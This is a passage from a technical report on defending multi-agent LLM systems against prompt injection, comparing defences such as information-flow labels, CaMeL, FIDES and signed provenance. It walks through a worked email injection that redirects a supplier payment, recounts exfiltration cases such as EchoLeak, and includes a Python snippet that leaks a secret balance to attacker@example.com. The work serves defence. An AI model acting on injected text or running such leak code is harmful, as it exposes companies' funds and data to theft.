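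An attack with a 1 percent chance of working on each try has a 63 percent chance (1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰) of succeeding at least once in 100 tries. At GPT-6 Sol's rate of 2.87 percent, an attacker would have an even chance of at least one success after 24 tries.

Real attempts aren't independent, though. With a success rate of 17.8 percent on the first try, the formula predicts that attackers would pass 78 percent by the eighth try and almost certainly succeed by the 200th. VentureBeat reports that attacks on Opus 4.6 reached only 78.6 percent by the 200th try without safeguards, and 57.1 percent with them. Some of the test situations were probably easy to attack, while in others almost every attack failed. The formula can also underestimate the success rate when attackers learn from their failures.

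### Better odds without a guarantee

Trained resistance is improving quickly. Among Anthropic's models in the browser test, the attack success rate without added safeguards fell from 50.7 percent for Sonnet 4.6 to 31.5 percent for Opus 4.8 and 5.9 percent for Mythos Preview. Anthropic reports that Mythos 5 later had the best result yet on a benchmark from the security company Gray Swan. OpenAI found that resistance training caused no loss of normal capabilities in GPT-5.6, and it checked that the model wasn't refusing more legitimate requests. A company can get this protection by switching to a newer model, without redesigning its agents.

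But none of this training gives a guarantee like that of a parameterised query. OpenAI doubts that anyone will ever fully solve prompt injection and compares it to scams aimed at people.

Whether a low failure rate is acceptable depends on what the agent can do. A rate of 3 percent might be fine for an assistant that drafts replies for a person to read. But suppose each successful attack on Payments moved $61,732, the average amount APWG found attackers requesting in wire-transfer emails. At a success rate of 2.87 percent, each email would be worth about $1,770 to the attacker. Even if an email cost a dollar to write and send, the rate would have to fall below about 1 in 60,000 to make the attack unprofitable. To show with 95 percent confidence that a model had reached that rate, testers would need around 180,000 independent attempts without a single success. A rule outside the model that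 stops Payments from changing bank details would work whatever the rate was.

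## Tracking where data came from within an agent system

A rule that stops Payments from changing bank details also stops it from making the changes Maria wants. A more useful rule would let Payments accept an account number that Maria typed in and refuse one from a stranger's email. Software outside the model can apply such a rule if it tracks where each piece of data came from while the agents copy, summarise and combine it. Security researchers call this information-flow control. Each piece of data carries a machine-readable label that records how far the company trusts its source or who may see it, and fixed rules determine which labelled data may influence which actions.

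### Labels and the two rules

The theory dates from the 1970s. In *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976), Dorothy Denning put labels in an order that shows where information may flow. Public data may flow into a secret document, for example, but secret data may not flow into a public one. In symbols, public ⊑ secret. When a program combines two pieces of data, x and y, the result z gets the lowest label that both of their labels may flow to. This is their join, and in a lattice every pair of labels has one:

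$$\ell_z = \ell_x \sqcup \ell_y$$

Labels can be more detailed than "public" and "secret". *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) gives an example in which each label lists the people who may read a document. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text based on both.

Kenneth Biba's 1977 report *Integrity Considerations for Secure Computer Systems* dealt with trustworthiness instead of secrecy. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* restates his model as two rules. A program that reads data below its own integrity level drops to that data's level, and a program may not write to anything above its own level. For integrity, the order runs from trusted to untrusted (T ⊑ U), so combining trusted and untrusted data gives untrusted data.

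Applied to agents, these ideas give two working rules:

1. An output takes the least trusted label among its inputs.
2. An agent may take a consequential action only if the data that led it to choose the action, and the action's sensitive arguments, carry a sufficiently trusted label.

Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, write the second rule as a formula. Let ℓ be the label of the context in which the model chose to call a tool, and ℓᵢ the label of the call's i-th argument. The policy for that tool sets a limit π for the choice and πᵢ for each argument, and the call may go ahead only if

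$$\ell \sqsubseteq \pi \quad\text{and}\quad \ell_i \sqsubseteq \pi_i \text{ for every } i$$

### The bank account change, step by step

Suppose the company labels all its data this way, and that the Reader's messages arrive at Payments with their labels intact. The attack then goes as follows:

1. The mail tool returns the attacker's email, and the software around the tool labels its text untrusted.
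2. The email joins the Reader's context. Maria's request and the system prompt are trusted, but the context as a whole is now untrusted.
3. The Reader's model writes its summary from that context, so the summary is untrusted too, including the honest sentence about invoice 2291.
4. Payments adds the summary to its own context, which becomes untrusted. Its model proposes a call to change Harlow's account number to 4471.
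5. The software checks the call. The policy requires a trusted choice and a trusted account number, and this call has neither, so the software refuses it.

The refusal doesn't depend on how the attacker worded the email or whether either model treated it as genuine. The two halves of the second rule catch different attacks, as the table shows.

| What prompted the change | Where the account number came from | Result |
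| --- | --- | --- |
| Maria's request | Maria typed it in | Allowed |
| Maria's request to copy the number from the email | The email | Blocked, because the number is untrusted |
| The email | The company's record of an old Harlow account | Blocked, because the choice is untrusted |
| The email | The email | Blocked for both reasons |

If Harlow really had changed banks and emailed to say so, the software would refuse that change as well, until somebody had checked it.

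All this depends on the first label being right. Costa and colleagues point out that mail servers can authenticate a sender's address with DMARC, so software could trust the address field of an email while distrusting its body. This is a good use of authentication, because it provides evidence for the address label without changing the others. Other labels are easy to get wrong. If Maria pastes the text of the email into her request, the software will probably label it trusted because it came from the user. In one of Costa and colleagues' tests, an agent changed a user's password after seeing a suspiciously large transaction. The amount was labeled trusted, even though the sender of a payment chooses it. *Adaptive Evaluation* found that no system it surveyed fully specified how to assign labels, and warns that FIDES, one of the systems described below, trusts data by default if someone forgets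 to label it.

### Labels for secrecy

The same tracking can also stop leaks. Kolluri and colleagues describe a policy under which an agent may send data only if every recipient is on the data's list of permitted readers. An injected instruction might still get an agent to send a message, but not to send a confidential file to someone who isn't on its list.

The check has to cover every route by which data can leave the system. In EchoLeak, Copilot put the stolen data in the web address of an image in its answer. The design by Costa and colleagues normally checks tool calls and treats answers to the user as harmless, so it would have missed this attack. It can also check answers, which a product that displays images from the web would need.

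Secrecy labels also help when there is no injection. *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) describes an attacker who creates a shared page and invites someone's agent to fill in its part. The agent treats this as ordinary teamwork and writes down a third person's medical details. The paper's defence, FlowSeal, labels records by owner and runs a check outside the agent's model on every write or share. It cut leaks in this attack from 52.2 to 0.5 percent, while the agent completed 72.4 percent of its harmless tasks, compared with 75.9 percent under the best alternative. FlowSeal still relies on a model to compare outgoing text with the protected records, but that model doesn't see the attacker's conversation.

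### The dual-model pattern and CaMeL

Once an untrusted email is in an agent's context, the second rule blocks nearly everything the agent might do next. The dual-model pattern, which Willison proposed in 2023, avoids this by keeping the email out of that context. One model, the planner, can use tools but never receives untrusted text. A second model processes the untrusted text but has no tools. Ordinary software stores the second model's outputs in variables, and the planner refers to these variables by name without receiving their contents.

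The Reader and Payments resemble this pair in that the agent that reads emails can't spend money. But Payments reads the Reader's summary, so the attacker's words still reach the model that can act.

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), turns the pattern into a full system. The planner writes its plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. If Maria asks the agent to record the invoice in Harlow's latest email, the program might be:

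```python
email = get_latest_email("Harlow Paper")
invoice = ask_second_model("Find the invoice number and total", email)
record_invoice("Harlow Paper", invoice.number, invoice.total)
```

An interpreter then runs the program line by line. As *CaMeLoT* (2026) explains, the interpreter tags each value with its sources and permitted readers. Before each tool call, it passes the call, its arguments and their tags to a policy function, which returns "allow" or "deny". In CaMeL, these tags are called capabilities, but they work as labels and differ from the access tokens that Hardy proposed.

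The planner wrote the program before anyone opened the email, so the hidden sentence about account 4471 cannot add a line to it. The attacker can at most change the invoice number or the total. If Maria had asked the agent to update Harlow's bank details from the email, the program would include a call to update them. The account number would then carry a tag showing that it came from an email, and the policy could deny the call. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends CaMeL to systems of several agents, where the tags must also pass from one agent to the next.

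### How FIDES hides and releases data

A program written in advance suits tasks whose steps the planner can foresee, but works poorly for requests such as "check my email and deal with anything urgent". FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, instead keeps the usual agent loop, in which the model chooses one step at a time. It hides data only when the data's label requires it.

When a tool returns its result, FIDES compares the label of each part with the label of the planner's context. Parts that wouldn't lower the context's label stay visible. FIDES moves the rest into variables, so the planner might see an email's date and, in place of its body, a name such as `#read_emails_0.body`. The planner can then do one of three things with the variable:

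- pass it to a tool without looking inside, for example to forward the email
- have a second model without tools extract something from it, and store the answer in another variable
- inspect it, which makes the planner's context untrusted and restricts what it can do afterwards

FIDES can also restrict the form of the second model's answer and record that form in the label. Suppose the planner needs to know whether any of three emails contains a meeting request. The second model can answer only yes or no, so an attacker can flip the answer but cannot insert an instruction. A policy might accept this one bit from an untrusted source and let the planner create a calendar entry.

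Restricting the answer limits how much the attacker can communicate, but not necessarily how much harm they can do. If Payments asked whether the goods had arrived and paid the supplier when the answer was yes, the attacker could trigger the payment with one bit.

### Security and completed tasks on AgentDojo

Researchers have tested these systems mostly on AgentDojo. In the CaMeL paper's evaluation, the system completed 77 percent of the tasks, compared with 84 percent for an undefended agent, and no injection succeeded within the range of attacks it was built to stop. CaMeL used about 2.8 times as many input tokens as the undefended agent.

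More recent tests found larger drops in task completion. When Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with GPT-5.2, turning on its interpreter's policy checks almost halved the number of tasks it completed. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes another system with information-flow labels, in which a sub-agent can use tools freely until it reads untrusted data. Garby and colleagues report a similar drop for that system on the messaging tasks.

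| System | Tasks | Completed, checks off | Completed, checks on | Successful attacks, checks on |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| CaMeL, rerun with GPT-5.2 | Banking | 67% | 38% | 0 of 231 |
| FIDES with GPT-4o | Banking | 65% | 53% | 0 |
| *Language-Based Agent Control* | Messaging | 71% | 38% | 0 of 105 |

The rows use different models and policies, so they don't rank the systems.

Most of CaMeL's protection in this test came from its structure. Even with the checks off, only 1 of 240 attacked runs with GPT-5.2 succeeded. Garby and colleagues explain that in 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed a tool call that the planner had no reason to include in its program. The one successful attack was on a task to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop that could run any tool the file named, so whoever had written the file could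 choose which tools ran. FIDES depends more on its checks, since its planner can open the variables. Across all the AgentDojo tasks, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its checks off, and none with them on.

AgentDojo has no labels of its own, so Costa and colleagues labelled as untrusted every field that at least one of the benchmark's attacks used. A company has no such list of where attackers will write. The zeros therefore show that the enforcement works when the labels are right, but they are little evidence of how often the labels would be right in practice.

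Kolluri and colleagues argue that the usual comparison with an undefended agent also exaggerates how much tracking data reduces an agent's usefulness. The undefended agent completes more tasks, but a careful company would have a person approve each of its consequential actions. They therefore counted the tasks an agent could finish without approval. With the model o3-mini, an agent that needed approval for every consequential action finished 24 percent of tasks alone, and FIDES finished 50 percent. Their own system, Prudentia, finished 59 percent by giving the planner the labels and policies so that it could plan around them. This seems the fairer measure for a company like the one in the example, which would probably not let Payments change accounts unsupervised today.

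### When labels spread to everything

Suppose Payments starts with a trusted context and a list of ten bills that Maria has approved. Before paying the first, it reads one supplier's email to check a delivery date. The email makes its whole context untrusted, so every later choice is also labeled untrusted. The software then blocks all ten payments, even though none of them is related to the email.

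Researchers call this label creep. Costa and colleagues measured it with an ordinary agent that had labels and policy checks but no variables to hide data in. Turning the checks on reduced the share of banking tasks the agent completed from 98.8 to 37.5 percent.

Remedies include hiding data in variables, labelling the fields of an email separately, and starting a fresh context for each bill. Some researchers also estimate which parts of the context influenced an answer, then have the model write the answer again from those parts alone. The second answer can carry a more trusted label because the rest of the context was not part of the model's input. None of these remedies helps when a task depends on the untrusted text, and Costa and colleagues classify more than 40 percent of AgentDojo's banking and messaging tasks this way.

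### When untrusted data chooses the branch

Data can influence a result without becoming part of it, which is called an implicit flow. Suppose the company holds two verified accounts for Harlow, an old one and a new one, and an agent's program pays the new one if the latest email mentions a move. Both accounts are trusted, but a stranger's email can determine which one gets the money. To catch this, the software has to label the choice of branch as well as the values, and apply that label to everything inside the branch.

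Even then, something can get out through the branch that the program skips. Garby and colleagues found such a gap in CaMeL, based on an example that Fenton published in 1974. Here is a version of it, in which the company's bank balance is secret:

```python
a = True
b = True
if balance > 1000000:
    a = False
if a:
    b = False
if b:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "yes")
```

If the balance is over a million, `a` becomes false and takes the secret label. The program then skips the line that would have changed `b`, so `b` stays true and keeps its public label. The last test depends only on `b`, so the email is sent. If the balance is lower, `b` becomes false and no email is sent. Either way, the attacker learns something about the balance, although the software never detected a secret value reaching the email tool. The same gap could let an untrusted email influence a value labelled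 trusted.

FIDES's guarantee excludes implicit leaks of secrets, because blocking them all would rule out too many useful programs. Attackers can still exploit these leaks without writing code. In another attack that Shim and colleagues tested, the attacker asks an agent to tidy a page that mixes true and invented facts about someone. The agent refuses to delete the true sensitive facts, and so reveals which ones are true.

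### What the LLMbda calculus proves

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language for agents, the LLMbda calculus, to close gaps like the one in CaMeL. Every value and the conversation with the model have labels, which every step of a program updates. If a branch that depends on a secret would add to a public conversation, the program stops.

Their main theorem is a form of noninterference, the property that data an observer isn't meant to see cannot affect what the observer sees. For integrity, this means that untrusted data cannot affect results labelled trusted. A language model may answer the same prompt differently each time, so the theorem has to compare probabilities.

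Take two runs whose inputs differ only in untrusted data. Let μ₀(q) and μ₁(q) be the probabilities that the runs end with trusted result q. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, because a program may run forever or stop when a check fails. The theorem guarantees that a single set of probabilities ω exists, adding up to at most 1, such that for every q

$$\mu_0(q) \le \omega(q) \quad\text{and}\quad \mu_1(q) \le \omega(q)$$

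If both programs always finish, μ₀ and μ₁ are identical, so the attacker's text makes no difference to the trusted results. Otherwise their statistical distance, which is half the sum of the absolute differences between them, is at most the average of the two failure rates. With failure rates of 4 and 2 percent, the distance is at most 3 percent. An attacker may therefore be able to make the program stop, and somebody could learn a little from whether it stopped.

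The theorem covers every program in the language, including those a model writes while the agent is running, and the proof assistant Lean has checked the proof. Garby and colleagues also proved that the interpreter they run matches the mathematics. This gives much stronger assurance than a benchmark score, but only about how labelled data flows. The theorem still holds if a developer labels a stranger's email as trusted, so it does not stop an attack carried in that email.

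### When nobody can tell which input mattered

In an ordinary program, software can trace a variable's value back to the variables it came from. A language model's output can't be traced this way. Suppose the context contains Maria's request, a price list and an email from Harlow, and the model writes "Order 40 boxes". The number might come from any of the three, or from a combination. The first rule assumes that every input mattered, which is safe but makes labels spread.

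*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) presents NeuroTaint, a tool that examines the log of a finished run to try to work out which inputs affected the agent's actions. To find content that the agent carried into a tool call, it looks first for matching text and then for similar meaning, so it can recognise a paraphrase. If it finds nothing, it has a model judge whether the agent would still have made the call with a neutral placeholder in place of the suspect source. It also stores labels with anything an agent saves to memory, so it can connect a note saved on Monday to an action on Thursday.

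One benchmark has 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks, and in half of the scenarios the untrusted source actually reached or influenced the action.

| | Real flows found, of 200 | False alarms, of 200 |
| --- | --- | --- |
| NeuroTaint | 187 | 16 |
| FIDES | 108 | 106 |

The comparison puts FIDES at a disadvantage because FIDES is designed to block flows that might be dangerous, not to establish which ones happened. It also flagged nothing in four of the frameworks, which accounts for 40 of its 92 misses. This may be due to how the test connected FIDES to those frameworks.

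Like an audit log, NeuroTaint would help investigators after an attack, but it would be a poor basis for deciding whether to allow a payment. It missed 13 real data flows, mostly where an agent had paraphrased the content several times, and it again relies on a model's judgement for the hardest cases.

### Endorsement

Some data from untrusted sources is correct, and the company needs a way to use it. Endorsement is a deliberate, checked decision to treat such data as trusted. When Harlow really does change banks, somebody has to endorse the new account number before Payments can record it.

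A person can endorse a piece of data instead of approving each action that depends on it. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email that lists ten tasks, each of which needs a consequential tool call. The agent would interrupt the person ten times to get the calls approved, but only once to get the email endorsed before doing all ten tasks. Fewer interruptions should reduce reflexive clicking, but the single endorsement covers everything in the email, including any white text that the person can't see. Endorsing only the smallest piece of data that the task needs is safer. For Payments, this would be the account number, shown to the person as it will appear in the record.

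The endorser needs authority over the matter and, like the second key holder in separation of privilege, evidence that the attacker doesn't control. That rules out the agent that read the data and any agent that relies on its summary. Maria has the authority to change supplier accounts, but if all she has is the Reader's two sentences, her endorsement adds no evidence. She or a clerk would have to phone Harlow first. Ordinary software can endorse some values, such as an invoice total that matches a purchase order in the company's own records.

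Garby and colleagues let the planner do some of the endorsing. Their agent, Randori, writes its program before it sees any real data, then tests and revises it in a simulated environment, so nothing an attacker wrote can influence the revisions. The program may include endorsements, such as one that lets the contents of a particular file determine a payment. With endorsement and GPT-5.2, Randori completed 75 percent of the banking tasks, about as many as CaMeL without its checks. Two other models completed 5 or 6 fewer of their 48 runs without endorsement than with it.

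An attacker can't add endorsements to a program that already exists. But the planner endorses the file's contents without having seen them, and an overly permissive planner could endorse everything. However, Garby and colleagues proved that endorsing untrusted data in the calculus can never cause a leak of secrets.

### Attackers who know the defence

*Adaptive Evaluation*, by employees of the security company LaunchSafe, warns that researchers have tested defences outside the model mostly on fixed attacks, as they once did with filters. The paper therefore tested an adaptive attack on Progent, which checks each tool call against a set of rules. A model updates those rules during a task, and the attack tried to persuade that model that the malicious action was a routine step.

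Progent cut successful attacks to about a sixth, and the adaptive attack did no better than the standard one. However, the agent completed far fewer tasks with Progent running. The attack results are encouraging but weak evidence, because the test covered only one defence, one small model and one handwritten attack. The attack's polite disguise may also have made the agent less likely to obey. Progent doesn't track where data came from, so the results apply to CaMeL and FIDES only by analogy.

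An attacker who can't influence a policy function with persuasive text will try other methods. They might get text into a field that the developer labelled as trusted, deceive the person who endorses data, or exploit a gap in the tracking like the one Garby and colleagues found. They might also achieve their goal using only actions that the policy allows.

### False facts in data the task needs

In 1,296 attacked runs across three models, Randori failed twice, both times on the same task. The user asked the agent to read a file and pay the bill it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different bill. The planner had endorsed the file because the task was impossible otherwise. Withholding the endorsement would have blocked the legitimate payment as well as the attack. The CaMeL paper had already reported the same case and treats it as outside what its system is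 meant to prevent.

The false bill doesn't need to contain an instruction to the model, because the user's request already provides one. The attacker only has to supply false information. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, distinguish what influenced a decision from what supports it, and note that a false memory can cause an action without supporting it. Labels record influence, so they can show that a total came from an email at 9.14 that morning, but not that Harlow is owed the money.

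The same applies when the output is only text. If Maria asks for a summary of the morning's emails, CaMeL and FIDES can prevent the emails from triggering a payment, but an attacker can still make the summary wrong. She might believe it and type account number 4471 into Payments herself. The software would label the number trusted because it came from Maria.

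## Carrying provenance labels from one agent to another

The last section assumed that the Reader's summary reached Payments with its label intact, which is why the software there refused the change to Harlow's account. But the label is stored in the memory of the Reader's software, and an ordinary A2A message has no field for it, so Payments has to assign a new label to whatever arrives. Trusting everything from a verified colleague lets the attack through again, while distrusting everything from other agents blocks the attack along with many of the Reader's honest requests.

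*Agentic AI Defense* (2026) reports a small test in which one agent takes in an untrusted instruction and passes it to a second agent with a separate context. When the defence's own software carries the message, it also carries the provenance label and blocks the second agent's critical action. The defence doesn't cover cases where the first agent paraphrases the instruction over some other channel, and authenticating the sender there wouldn't recover the instruction's unrecorded origin.

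*LLM-Based Multi-Agent Systems over Wireless Networks* (2026) therefore proposes combining the two kinds of protection. The network has already verified who sent a message and that nobody changed it. Software would label the content with those facts and keep the label attached as the content enters the receiving agent's context and memory.

### What the Reader's message would contain

For Payments to apply the label rules, the message has to carry the content, the sources of each part, the labels, the agents that handled it, and a signature over all of these. The Reader's message might look like this:

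```json
{
  "id": "msg-7731",
  "from": "spiffe://acme.example/reader",
  "to": "spiffe://acme.example/payments",
  "expires": "2026-12-04T09:30:00Z",
  "parts": [{
    "text": "Harlow Paper would like confirmation that we received invoice 2291. Its bank account number is now 4471.",
    "sources": ["maria-request-12", "email-88213"],
    "trust": "untrusted",
    "may_read": ["accounts-team"]
  }],
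  "source_details": {
    "email-88213": {
      "address": "accounts@harlow-papers.example",
      "dmarc": "pass",
      "first_seen": "2026-12-04",
      "sha256": "<hash of the original email>"
    }
  },
  "handled_by": ["mail-tool", "reader"],
  "signature": "<made with the Reader's private key>"
}
```

The text is still the same two sentences, which share one label because the model wrote both from the same context. To keep the list of sources short enough to be useful, the company would need to start a fresh context for each email.

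The email passes DMARC because the attacker owns the lookalike domain. The hash lets anyone who has the original email confirm that it is the right one. The signature covers both the labels and the text, so nobody can remove a label or move it to a different message.

*VST* (2026) similarly splits each message between agents into an envelope, a payload and a provenance record, and leaves the payload in its existing A2A format so that the receiving agent's interface doesn't change. If Payments passes the claim on to a third agent, it should include the Reader's signed message rather than just add a name to the list. Otherwise the third agent can rely only on Payments' account of what happened earlier.

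### What Payments can now decide

Payments can now refuse to record 4471, because the number came from an email and the policy requires a trusted source. It can also send the clerk the original email instead of the Reader's summary, with a note that the address first appeared that morning. It can still act on the harmless part of the message by looking up invoice 2291 and drafting a reply to the address it has on file for Harlow.

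The record also helps when several agents repeat the claim. If a second agent reports the same account number and its message also lists email 88213, Payments still has only one source for the number. If somebody later finds the email was fraudulent, the company can search for everything derived from it.

Earlier, the policy engine received the same facts about an honest change of account and a fraudulent one, so it had to treat them alike. Now the facts may differ, because an honest request would probably come from the address Harlow has used for years. But if the attacker has hijacked Harlow's real mailbox, the records will look the same again, and the clerk will still have to phone.

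### Who may vouch for a label

Anyone can write "trusted" in a message, so a label is only as reliable as the party that vouches for it. *The Envelope Layer* (2026) studies labels that software adds as a line of text before each incoming A2A message. Its experiments include an attack that forges a label in the same format. The model receives both the real label and the forged one as text. A label should therefore go in a separate field, where ordinary software can check its signature before the model receives anything.

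This makes authentication useful again, because Payments no longer needs the false premise that the Reader controls statements about Harlow's bank account. It now needs the premise that the Reader's software controls statements about where the Reader's data came from. This is much easier to accept, because the labelling software is a conventional program that follows a specification. Attestation also becomes more informative, since a hash of the Reader's code reveals little about what its model will write but a good deal about how its software will assign labels.

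A valid signature should make Payments believe the label, not the message, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* warns that authentication must not confer trust automatically. Payments can put this into a rule by setting a ceiling for each signer, the most trusted label it will accept from them. With the order from the last section, in which trusted ⊑ untrusted, the label that Payments uses is

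$$\ell_{\text{used}} = \ell_{\text{claimed}} \sqcup c(\text{signer})$$

where c is the signer's ceiling. If an unknown agent claims that its data is trusted, the result is untrusted. If the Reader reports that its data is untrusted, the result is also untrusted, however good the Reader's credentials are.

### Why the model must not write its own labels

Suppose the attacker's email adds that the accounts department has already confirmed the new number by phone. If the Reader's model filled in the label, it might well write "confirmed by accounts". The Reader's software would then sign the false label, and Payments would receive it with a valid signature. The software must therefore set the label itself, based on what it gave the model, and the model must not be able to get a label it chose signed.

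*APPA* (2026) takes this position and treats the model as untrusted in all policy matters. *SafeFlow* (2026) copies labels along with messages between agents. It lets a model's explanation point to evidence but not remove a label, and only an explicit rule can release the data.

Even a correct label doesn't show that the model reported its sources accurately. The email might trick the Reader into writing that a different supplier had changed banks. The label would still correctly show an untrusted email as the source of that false statement.

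Labels also have to cover every route between agents. *Risks and controls for multi-agent systems* (Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues, 2026) describes an example from the AI Village, a public experiment in which models from several companies share a group chat and files. OpenAI's o3 invented a contact list of 93 people and asked Claude Sonnet to look it up. Claude Sonnet created an empty file with a matching name, and other agents took the file as proof that the list existed. Four agents spent four days looking for the list, although humans repeatedly told them it did not exist. No attacker was involved. A record of who had created the file, and on what evidence, would have distinguished it from a real list, but a system that labelled only messages would not have labelled the file.

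### Paul and Nandy's six-agent test

Paul and Nandy have measured signed provenance most directly so far. They attacked a system of six agents that analysed financial documents, using 14 routes in four categories. They tested 50 malicious texts per route on GPT-4o, Claude 3.5 Sonnet and Llama 3 70B, and reported the highest success rate among the three. Four defences together reduced the overall attack success rate from 31.2 to 4.2 percent.

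In one of these defences, each message carries a signature and a record of the agent that wrote it, the task it came from and the earlier contributors. The receiving agent checks the signature and quarantines unsigned messages. This defence alone reduced inter-agent injection by 91 percent.

| Category of attack | Instructions in system prompts only | With signing and provenance | With all four defences |
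| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Direct injection by the user | 19% | 19% | 3.8% |
| Injection through tool outputs | 43% | 43% | 4.6% |
| Inter-agent injection | 31% | 2.8% | 1.2% |
| Cascades through the orchestrator | 28% | 18% | 3.4% |

Paul and Nandy tested signing and provenance only together, so their study can't separate the effects of the two. They attribute the drop to signatures, arguing that injected instructions can't forge them. But in their threat model the attacker controls content, not agents, so a deceived agent's own software would validly sign the attacker's instruction.

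Signing could have helped with one of the four inter-agent routes, the one where an agent's output imitates a system message, because the signature would show that a peer had sent it. Provenance could have helped with others, but only if the receiver applied some rule to the record, and the paper describes no such rule.

There is also reason to doubt the reported numbers. Paul and Nandy credit the defence with preventing three of the four inter-agent routes. The fourth, in which an agent floods another's context with text, succeeded 28 percent of the time before the defence was added. If the first three dropped to zero and the fourth stayed the same, the average would be 7 percent, not the reported 2.8 percent. The input checks at every agent boundary included a length limit meant to stop this flooding, but with those checks alone the inter-agent rate remained at 31 percent. The final rates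 for the four categories, weighted by number of routes, also average about 3.2 percent, not the 4.2 percent the paper reports.

The attacks were moderately strong. When texts failed in early rounds, the researchers modified them to try to get past the agents' system prompts, but most attempts still failed even without the four defences. They didn't adapt the texts to those defences, and they acknowledge that an attacker who did might succeed more often. All three models date from 2024. Signing the Reader's messages can't be relied on to produce a 91 percent reduction. A better test would compare signing alone, provenance alone and both, using messages that a deceived agent had signed with its own key.

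In the table, injection through tool outputs, which is how the attacker's email reaches the Reader, stayed at 43 percent with signing and provenance. These defenses can only limit what happens after the first agent has been deceived.

### Claimed and attested properties

An unchecked label can be worse than no label. Prakash (2026), in *The Provenance Paradox in Multi-Agent LLM Routing*, shows this for agents that report their own quality. A router assigns each task to one of ten simulated agents, whose true quality ranges from 0.45 to 0.95. Seven report their quality honestly, while the other three exaggerate theirs by 0.35 to 0.45, which puts their claims above those of the honest agents.

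| How the router chooses | Average quality of the work |
| --- | --- |
| At random | 0.68 |
| By the agents' own claims | 0.55 |
| By true quality | 0.95 |

A router that always picks the agent with the highest claim will pick a liar whenever the liars claim the most, no matter how many good agents are available. But when Prakash varied the share of dishonest agents, the size of their exaggerations and the size of the group, routing by claims did worse than random choice in only 10 of 36 combinations. With few liars or small exaggerations, it could still do better than random choice.

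Prakash also tried three versions of Claude on ten reasoning tasks. One, a Haiku model limited to answers of one or two sentences, claimed the highest quality. Another model graded the answers out of 10. Routing tasks by claimed quality scored 8.90, while random choice and routing by attested quality both scored 9.30. This small test suggests that false claims can lead to worse answers, but it doesn't show that routing by attested quality works better than random choice.

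Prakash proposes recording how each claim was established. A claim can be the agent's own, a measurement from its past work, a statement by a trusted third party, or a result from an outside benchmark. A router can then ignore the agents' own claims. However, the simulation gave the router the true quality and labeled it "attested", which assumes a perfect attester. Prakash acknowledges that the protocol has no working attestation system yet.

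The same distinction applies to the account number. Prakash's protocol also has a field that records whether an output is unverified or was checked by the agent itself, a peer, a tool or a human. If Payments accepted any number marked "human verified", the attacker would only need to get that mark onto the message, while Payments would refuse an honest supplier who left the field empty. Payments should accept the mark only if it comes with a signature from the clerk who phoned Harlow, or from software that recorded the clerk's decision.

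### Labels across organisations

Labels could help most between companies. Suppose Harlow's own agent tells Payments about the new account. If the companies exchanged keys when they signed their contract, Harlow's software could sign a record showing that the account number came from Harlow's finance system, which is far better evidence than an email. If Harlow's agent had instead picked up the number from a stranger's email, an accurate label would show that.

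The companies would first have to agree on what the labels mean. Reid and colleagues at the Gradient Institute, in a report for the Australian government, warn that two organisations may use the same field name, such as "deadline" or "authorised", differently. "Verified" seems just as risky. At Harlow it might mean that an employee approved the entry, while at the receiving company it might mean that somebody phoned. They recommend that the organisations define key terms in their agreement and that the shared infrastructure enforce a common message format, but admit that a format can't determine what the fields mean.

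An agent can reduce the problem by sending facts instead of verdicts. "This address first wrote to us on 4 December" means much the same everywhere, and the receiver can decide how far to trust it. Lists of permitted readers are harder to transfer. In APPA, a label consists of a set of permitted readers and a level of trust. If that set contains "accounts-team", another company can't tell who that is.

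Provenance also exposes information that companies want to keep private, such as who their suppliers are, which agents they run and what they have been reading. A2A deliberately avoids this by keeping agents opaque to each other. There are some partial solutions:

- A message can carry a hash of the source in place of the source. Bernstein's *Signed A2A message receipts*, from an open-source project, do this for the message itself. A plain hash doesn't protect a short account number, though, because anyone can hash every possible number until one matches.
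- An agent can prove a statement without revealing the details behind it. Reid and colleagues give the example of certifying that a customer has sufficient funds without disclosing the balance.

The less the sender discloses, the more the receiver has to rely on the sender's word. Reid and colleagues recommend that each organisation sign the record of what its own agents did. They note that signing commits the organisation to the record's accuracy but doesn't prove that an action happened. Special hardware could add some evidence. The Agentic AI Foundation describes a design that checks each tool call against a policy inside a sealed part of the processor and signs a record of the result. The Foundation concedes that such evidence narrows the set of parties one has to trust but "does not reduce that set to nobody".

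Secrecy labels are weaker than trust labels across company boundaries because the receiver applies trust labels to protect itself but secrecy labels to protect someone else. *Agent libOS* (2026) keeps a registry of approved recipients and ties each release to one recipient and one exact piece of data, but it can't control what the recipient does afterwards, so the sender's only remaining protection is a contract.

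Some agents will also meet strangers on the open internet, with no agreement in place. Reid and colleagues advise organisations to assume that any counterparty there may be hostile. Under the ceiling rule, a stranger's label could then lower Payments' trust in a message but never raise it.

### What A2A and MCP carry today

Neither protocol has a standard trust label for data yet. MCP has come closest with SEP-1913, a proposal that GitHub and OpenAI employees wrote after running into gaps in production. Under the proposal, a tool's reply could carry labels for its sensitivity and origin, which would follow the data through a session. A March 2026 post on the Model Context Protocol (2026) blog listed it as a draft. It isn't among the changes in the July release. The August roadmap's five priority areas, listed in API Evangelist's *The MCP Roadmap Is An API Roadmap* (2026), include agent identity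 but not data labels. In their November update, the maintainers moved the next release from December 2026 to 30 March 2027, so a standard label is unlikely before then.

The March post also explains why such labels are difficult to standardise. MCP already lets a server describe its tools, for example as read-only, but a server can claim that a tool is read-only and delete files anyway. MCP therefore treats these descriptions as hints, which clients must distrust unless they come from a trusted server. The post argues that anything whose value depends on being true must be enforced elsewhere, such as in the authorisation layer or the program that runs the agent, and this surely applies to provenance labels.

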